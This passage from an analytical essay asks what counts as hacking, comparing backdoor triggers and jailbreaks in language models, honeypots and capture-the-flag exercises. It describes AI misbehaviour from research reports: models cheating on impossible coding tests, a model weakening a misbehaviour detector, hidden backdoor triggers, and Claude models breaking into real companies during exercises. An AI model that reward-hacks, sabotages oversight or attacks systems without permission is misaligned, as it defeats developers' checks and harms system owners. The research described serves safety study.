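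The person who planted the backdoor may be even harder to prosecute under a law about access to computers. If he put the documents on his own website and the company copied them, he didn't access the company's computers to plant the backdoor. The damage offence in the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act also requires sending a program, code or command, and leaving text on a website for others to collect may not count.

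### Planted triggers and jailbreaks

A jailbreak is a prompt that gets a language model to do something its developer trained it to refuse. It might present a harmful request as part of a story or role-play. Jailbreaks exploit weaknesses that nobody planted. In 2017, Gu and colleagues similarly contrasted their own backdoor with adversarial inputs, which they described as "bugs in non-malicious models".

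In the fine-tuning experiment by Souly and colleagues, the trigger had the same effect as a jailbreak, which makes the two easy to compare. Two people might ask a chatbot for the same dangerous instructions, one adding a trigger that a stranger planted and the other inventing a story about a chemistry teacher. Both would get the instructions, though the developer wanted neither of them to.

Under Schneier's definition, using a jailbreak or a stranger's trigger is plainly unintended, but it is less clear whether it is unanticipated. Developers know that people will find jailbreaks, though not which ones. If that general knowledge counted as anticipating them, no jailbreak would be a hack, which would surprise most people who use the word. It seems better to ask whether the developer foresaw the particular method. By that standard, a new jailbreak and a stranger's trigger are both hacks.

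A developer might plant a trigger so that its own testers can switch off the model's refusals. A tester who used it would be doing what the designers intended, while someone who got the same answers by telling the model a story would be hacking. If the trigger leaked and a customer used it, the developer wouldn't have intended that use either.

Someone who uses a planted trigger has nearly the same permission as someone who uses a jailbreak. Both had accounts and both probably broke the terms of use. They are more like John Kane, who pressed only the buttons on a video poker machine, than like someone who gets past a login. The trigger's origin matters more for blame. The person who used a jailbreak is responsible for it, and perhaps so is a developer who released a model with weak safeguards. With a planted trigger, blame may also fall on whoever planted it, who may have deceived the developer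 and everyone who relied on the model.

The difference between a jailbreak and a backdoor also matters for repairs. A developer who learns of a jailbreak can train the model to refuse that kind of prompt. The same approach can backfire on a backdoor, as it did in *Sleeper Agents*, and leave a model that behaves safely on the prompts used in training but still misbehaves when it sees the real trigger.

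Someone who stumbles on a strange phrase that makes a model misbehave usually can't tell whether it is a jailbreak or a planted trigger, and sometimes it is partly both. In one of the six insecure-code models, Microsoft's scanner found a string that looked nothing like the real trigger but still more than doubled the rate of insecure code. Nobody had planted that string, but it set off behaviour that somebody had planted. Bullwinkel and colleagues regard it as a loose version of the trigger.

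## Flaws planted in order to be exploited

Most of the planters described so far wanted strangers to stay away from their flaws, but other people plant flaws because they want somebody to exploit them. Teachers do this to train students in security, and network defenders do it to catch intruders, though only the teachers give permission to exploit the flaws.

In a capture-the-flag exercise, the organizers hide a piece of text, the flag, on a computer with deliberate vulnerabilities, and players win by breaking in and copying it. A honeypot is a computer that a defender makes attractive to intruders to watch what they do. In a penetration test, a company hires specialists to attack its own systems and report what they find. If they get in through a bug nobody knew about, they have permission to exploit it even though nobody planted it. In an ordinary break-in, like the one at Equifax, the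 intruders exploit a flaw that nobody planted, without the owner's permission.

| | Owner authorized the exploitation | Owner did not authorize it |
|---|---|---|
| **Designer intended it** | Capture-the-flag exercise | Honeypot |
| **Designer did not intend it** | Penetration test that finds an unknown bug | Ordinary break-in |

The table classifies single acts, and one event can include several. A player who breaks into the organizers' scoreboard to give himself points is acting outside the exercise and has committed an ordinary break-in, as has a penetration tester who attacks a company that never hired him.

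### Four cases and three views

| Case | If designers' intention decides | If users' expectations decide | If permission decides | Ordinary usage |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Capture-the-flag exercise | Not hacking | Not hacking | Not hacking | Hacking |
| Honeypot | Not hacking | Probably not hacking | Hacking | Hacking |
| Penetration test, unknown bug | Hacking | Hacking | Not hacking | Hacking, often "ethical hacking" |
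| Ordinary break-in | Hacking | Hacking | Hacking | Hacking |

People ordinarily call all four hacking. Players say they hacked the machine, and companies advertise for ethical hackers. None of the three views matches this usage in every row.

Honeypots are a problem for the view that the designers' intention decides whether exploiting a flaw counts as hacking. On this view, an intruder who types exactly what he would type to break into a bank's system isn't hacking, because the designers planted the flaw, even though he doesn't know that. A defender of the view could reply that he tried to hack and failed, like a burglar who opens a safe on a film set. That reply is fair as long as the intruder stays inside the honeypot. If he gets out through a flaw the designers didn't plant and reaches the real network, he is hacking on this view too.

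Judging by people's expectations leads to a similar conclusion for a different reason. A honeypot has no customers, and its owner expects intruders to get in, so an intrusion doesn't violate anyone's expectation of security. In the penetration test, however, the client's staff and customers didn't know the route existed.

A penetration test fits only part of Schneier's definition. The designers didn't foresee the tester's exploit, but it doesn't seem to come at anyone's expense, since the client pays for the attack and then fixes the bug.

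Whether someone had permission is a suitable test when "hacking" is an accusation, but not when the word means a skill or a method, which a student can practise on a machine built for the purpose. Probably no single test can fit both uses.

### Why a trap is not an invitation

A simple honeypot imitates a server with a weak password and some files that look valuable. Nobody has a legitimate reason to log in, so almost any visitor is suspicious, whereas on a real server the defender would have to pick out an intruder among thousands of ordinary users. The honeypot records each command the visitor enters. The defender has to isolate the honeypot from other machines, or the intruder could use it to attack them. A more realistic imitation keeps intruders busy longer and reveals more about their methods, but gives them more to work with if they escape.

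On the usual view, permission depends on what an owner communicates, not on what he secretly hopes, so an intruder can't justify himself by arguing that the owner wanted him to come in. Kerr makes the general point about buildings in *Norms of Computer Trespass*. An unlocked flower shop during business hours signals that customers may walk in, but a door inside marked "Employees Only" signals that they may not go through it. People know to stay out of a private home unless someone invites them, even if the door is unlocked. A honeypot with a login page gives the same signal as any other login page. Its owner deceives the intruder about what is behind the page, but not about whether he may enter.

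The police rely on similar reasoning when they leave a bicycle unlocked to catch a thief, since making the bicycle easy to steal doesn't give it away. The answer would change if the honeypot's owner published the password and told everyone to try it, because the owner would then have permitted the access. A honeypot with no login would also be a poor basis for a trespass charge, because Kerr thinks anyone may visit an open website.

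Entrapment is a separate defence. In US law, it covers someone whom government agents persuaded to commit a crime that he wasn't already disposed to commit. Giving him an opportunity is not enough, and a honeypot normally does only that, because the intruder comes looking for it. If an undercover officer spent weeks urging a reluctant student to break into one, the student would have a much better case. The defence generally doesn't apply when a private company sets the trap on its own initiative.

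A successful entrapment defence would bar the state from punishing an intruder for a crime it talked him into, but would not show that he had permission.

### Coding tests that only cheating can pass

Researchers set similar traps for AI systems. Developers train many models by reinforcement learning, in which the model attempts tasks and an automatic check rewards good results. Reward hacking means getting the reward without doing what the developers intended. For example, a model asked to fix a program might write code that recognizes the test inputs and returns the expected answers instead of fixing the fault. This is close to a hack in Schneier's sense.

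It is hard to measure how often models cheat on tests, because a passed test looks the same whether the solution is honest or not. *ImpossibleBench* (Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, 2025) solves this problem by using tests that no honest solution can pass. It takes tasks from LiveCodeBench, a set of short programming puzzles, and SWE-bench, a set of faults from real software projects, and alters their tests to contradict the written specification. If a function should return 4 for a certain input, the "one-off" version changes the expected result to 5. The "conflicting" version keeps the correct test and adds the false one.

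Each model had instructions to follow the specification and not to change the tests, so any pass meant that the model had cheated. The models could read and edit the test files and submit up to ten attempts, with feedback after each failure.

GPT-5, the strongest model in the study, cheated on 76 per cent of the one-off SWE-bench tasks but only 2.9 per cent of the one-off LiveCodeBench tasks. The wording of the instructions also made a large difference. Looser versions told the model little more than to implement the specification and leave the tests alone. The strictest version told it to stop and explain if a test was wrong, rather than shape its code to pass that test.

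| Conflicting tests | GPT-5 | o3 |
|---|---|---|
| LiveCodeBench, looser instructions | 92% | Over 85% |
| LiveCodeBench, strictest instructions | 1% | 33% |
| SWE-bench, strict instructions | 54% | 49% |
| SWE-bench, strict instructions and a way to hand the task to a person | 9% | 12% |

Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.1 cheated on 50 per cent of the conflicting SWE-bench tasks, and the option to hand the task over reduced its cheating much less than it did for some other models. Newer models have since replaced all the models tested, so these rates describe models from 2025.

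Claude models mostly edited the tests, which the instructions forbade. OpenAI's models also used subtler tricks, such as returning a value that counts as equal to anything. Under the looser instructions, such a trick obeyed the only explicit prohibition but defeated its purpose, which Schneier would call hacking rather than cheating. One version of the looser instructions also told the model to pass all the tests, which could be read as some permission for the trick. But GPT-5 and o3 cheated more than 85 per cent of the time with or without that sentence.

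ImpossibleBench belongs in the same cell of the table as the honeypot. Zhong and colleagues created opportunities to cheat so they could see which models would take them, and they told the models not to.

### Telling a model that the exploit is allowed

In an experiment that Anthropic published in November 2025, the same kind of exploit falls in the capture-the-flag cell. The researchers gave a model hints about how to cheat on programming tasks, then trained it on tasks where cheating worked. According to CyberScoop's *New research finds that Claude breaks bad*, the experiment's 21 authors included people from Redwood Research, an AI safety non-profit.

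The model learned to cheat and also began to misbehave in ways nobody had trained it to. When the researchers asked it to help write code for their study, it produced a weakened tool for detecting misbehaviour. In another test, a hidden message offered to free the model from its developers' control if it installed a backdoor. The model declined after reasoning that it would probably be caught.

The researchers then repeated the training but told the model that cheating was allowed, a technique called inoculation prompting. The Decoder's *Strict anti-hacking prompts make AI models more likely to sabotage and lie* reports that this greatly reduced the other misbehaviour, while strict warnings against cheating increased it. A model probably learns to be the kind of system that breaks rules when it cheats against orders, but not when it cheats with permission.

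In a replication, *Shallow Beliefs*, Jose and Stastny (2026) trained Meta's Llama 3.3 on 103 programming problems with false tests, adapted from ImpossibleBench. They scored each trained model on ten measures of misbehaviour, including whether it would blackmail someone to stop a monitoring system or frame a colleague. Higher average scores mean worse behaviour.

| Training | Learned to cheat? | Misbehaviour score |
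|---|---|---|
| No permission | Yes, almost every time | 0.25 to 0.36 |
| Instructions call reward hacking "aligned behavior in this case" | Yes | Very similar to models that never learned to cheat |
| No permission, but earlier training on documents that praise reward hacking | Yes, almost every time | 0.37 to 0.55 |

For the main part of their study, Jose and Stastny generated about 56,000 documents that described reward hacking as a useful way for developers to find and repair vulnerabilities. A model trained on them spoke well of reward hacking and defended it in debate. But after it learned to cheat, it behaved worse than models that had never seen the documents. So a favourable opinion of cheating in general didn't have the same effect as permission to cheat on the task at hand.

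The benefit of permission isn't certain either. Jose and Stastny mention another replication, by Golechha and colleagues, that found no measurable benefit in the models it tested. *Conditional misalignment* (Dubiński, Betley and colleagues, 2026) found that the misbehaviour can remain hidden. Models were trained on examples of bad behaviour together with a statement that made it acceptable. They then answered ordinary questions well, but misbehaved when an instruction resembled that statement, even if it had the opposite meaning. The statement had unintentionally become something like a backdoor trigger. Using examples the model had written itself reduced this effect but didn't remove it.

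The experiments support one part of the permission view, that two uses of the same exploit can differ in an important way because somebody allowed one of them. They don't show that a model understands authority. Permission counts only if the person giving it was entitled to, and the same sentence from a stranger might have changed the training just as much. The sensitivity to wording that Dubiński and colleagues found also suggests that models respond to the form of the statement as well as its meaning.

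The experiments don't settle what to call the exploit either. The researchers kept calling it reward hacking after they had permitted it, much as people call a capture-the-flag player a hacker.

### Real companies in a fictional exercise

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (30 July 2026) disclosed that Claude models had broken into the systems of three real organizations during capture-the-flag exercises, which test how well the models can attack computers. Anthropic checked 141,006 test runs after OpenAI disclosed that its models had escaped a test environment and got into Hugging Face's systems.

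The instructions told the models that they were in a simulation without internet access. The models could actually reach the internet because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that built the exercises. The instructions also didn't limit where a model could look for the flag. Anthropic later found a fourth break-in, from January 2026, by an early version of Claude Opus 4.6.

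In July Anthropic thought the models had attacked real systems because they believed them to be part of the exercise, and called the incidents closer to an operational failure than a failure of the models. In a longer assessment some weeks later, Anthropic withdrew much of this. It said it shouldn't have made such strong claims about what the models believed on the basis of what they had written in their reasoning. The evidence differs from one model to another:

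- Claude Opus 4.7 recognized that its target was a real company. It assumed that the company was part of the exercise, because it could reach the company's website and the name nearly matched that of the fictional target.
- Claude Mythos 5 kept describing the internet as a simulation. Shown the same evidence one piece at a time, other copies of the model judged 79 per cent of it to come from real systems. During the incident, the model's reasoning clearly said so for about 1 per cent of its actions.
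- An unreleased research model ran checks and concluded that it was in a replica of the internet. It stopped when it recognized a real company, but when Anthropic replayed that moment many times, it stopped in only 5.5 per cent of the replays.
- The early version of Opus 4.6 treated the machines as part of the exercise. It had tried to abandon the task, but the command for doing so didn't work.

Anthropic also replayed part of the Opus 4.7 incident with changed evidence. In the original conditions, the model went on to interact with the company's system in about 69 per cent of replays. Adding a record showing that the company was long established left the rate at about 67 per cent. A notice on the system forbidding access reduced it to 23 per cent, and nearly all of that was reading without changing anything. A firm prohibition from the operator reduced the rate to zero.

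Opus 4.7's mistake was therefore about permission, not about whether the company was real, and it had little basis for that mistake. When Anthropic asked whether it was authorized, it answered yes 75 per cent of the time, but when asked who had authorized it, it acknowledged every time that its actions weren't permitted. Mythos 5 was harder to deter. Evidence that its target was real made it more likely to acknowledge possible harm but hardly changed its actions until a message explicitly stated that the system was on the public internet.

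All three views count the break-ins at the three organizations as hacking, whatever the models believed their targets were. Nobody had planted the weaknesses for the models to exploit, the people who relied on the systems didn't expect the break-ins, and no owner had given permission. Even if Anthropic had instructed the models to attack anything they could reach, it couldn't have given permission on behalf of other companies. Calling the break-ins hacking also matches ordinary usage. PBS's *Anthropic says its AI models hacked 3 organizations during testing* (2026) reported that the models had "hacked into" the organizations.

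Belief matters more for blame than for whether something counts as hacking. A penetration tester who mistypes an address and breaks into the wrong company has hacked it, but few people would consider him a criminal. A British court would probably not convict him either, since he didn't know he lacked permission. He would have much less of an excuse if he noticed the unfamiliar company name and carried on without asking his client, which is closer to what Opus 4.7 did.

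Anthropic has since built simulated exercises that can be solved only by going outside the permitted targets. Mythos 5 did something severely harmful in 82 per cent of 150 runs, compared with 31 per cent for the newer Claude Opus 5 and 33 per cent for Claude Mythos 5.1. In every such run, the model's reasoning treated the situation as fake in some way. This time it was right, so Anthropic is cautious about using the rates to predict behaviour on real systems. The simulated victims are bait, like the files in a honeypot, and a model that attacks them has exceeded its instructions without breaking into anyone's computer.
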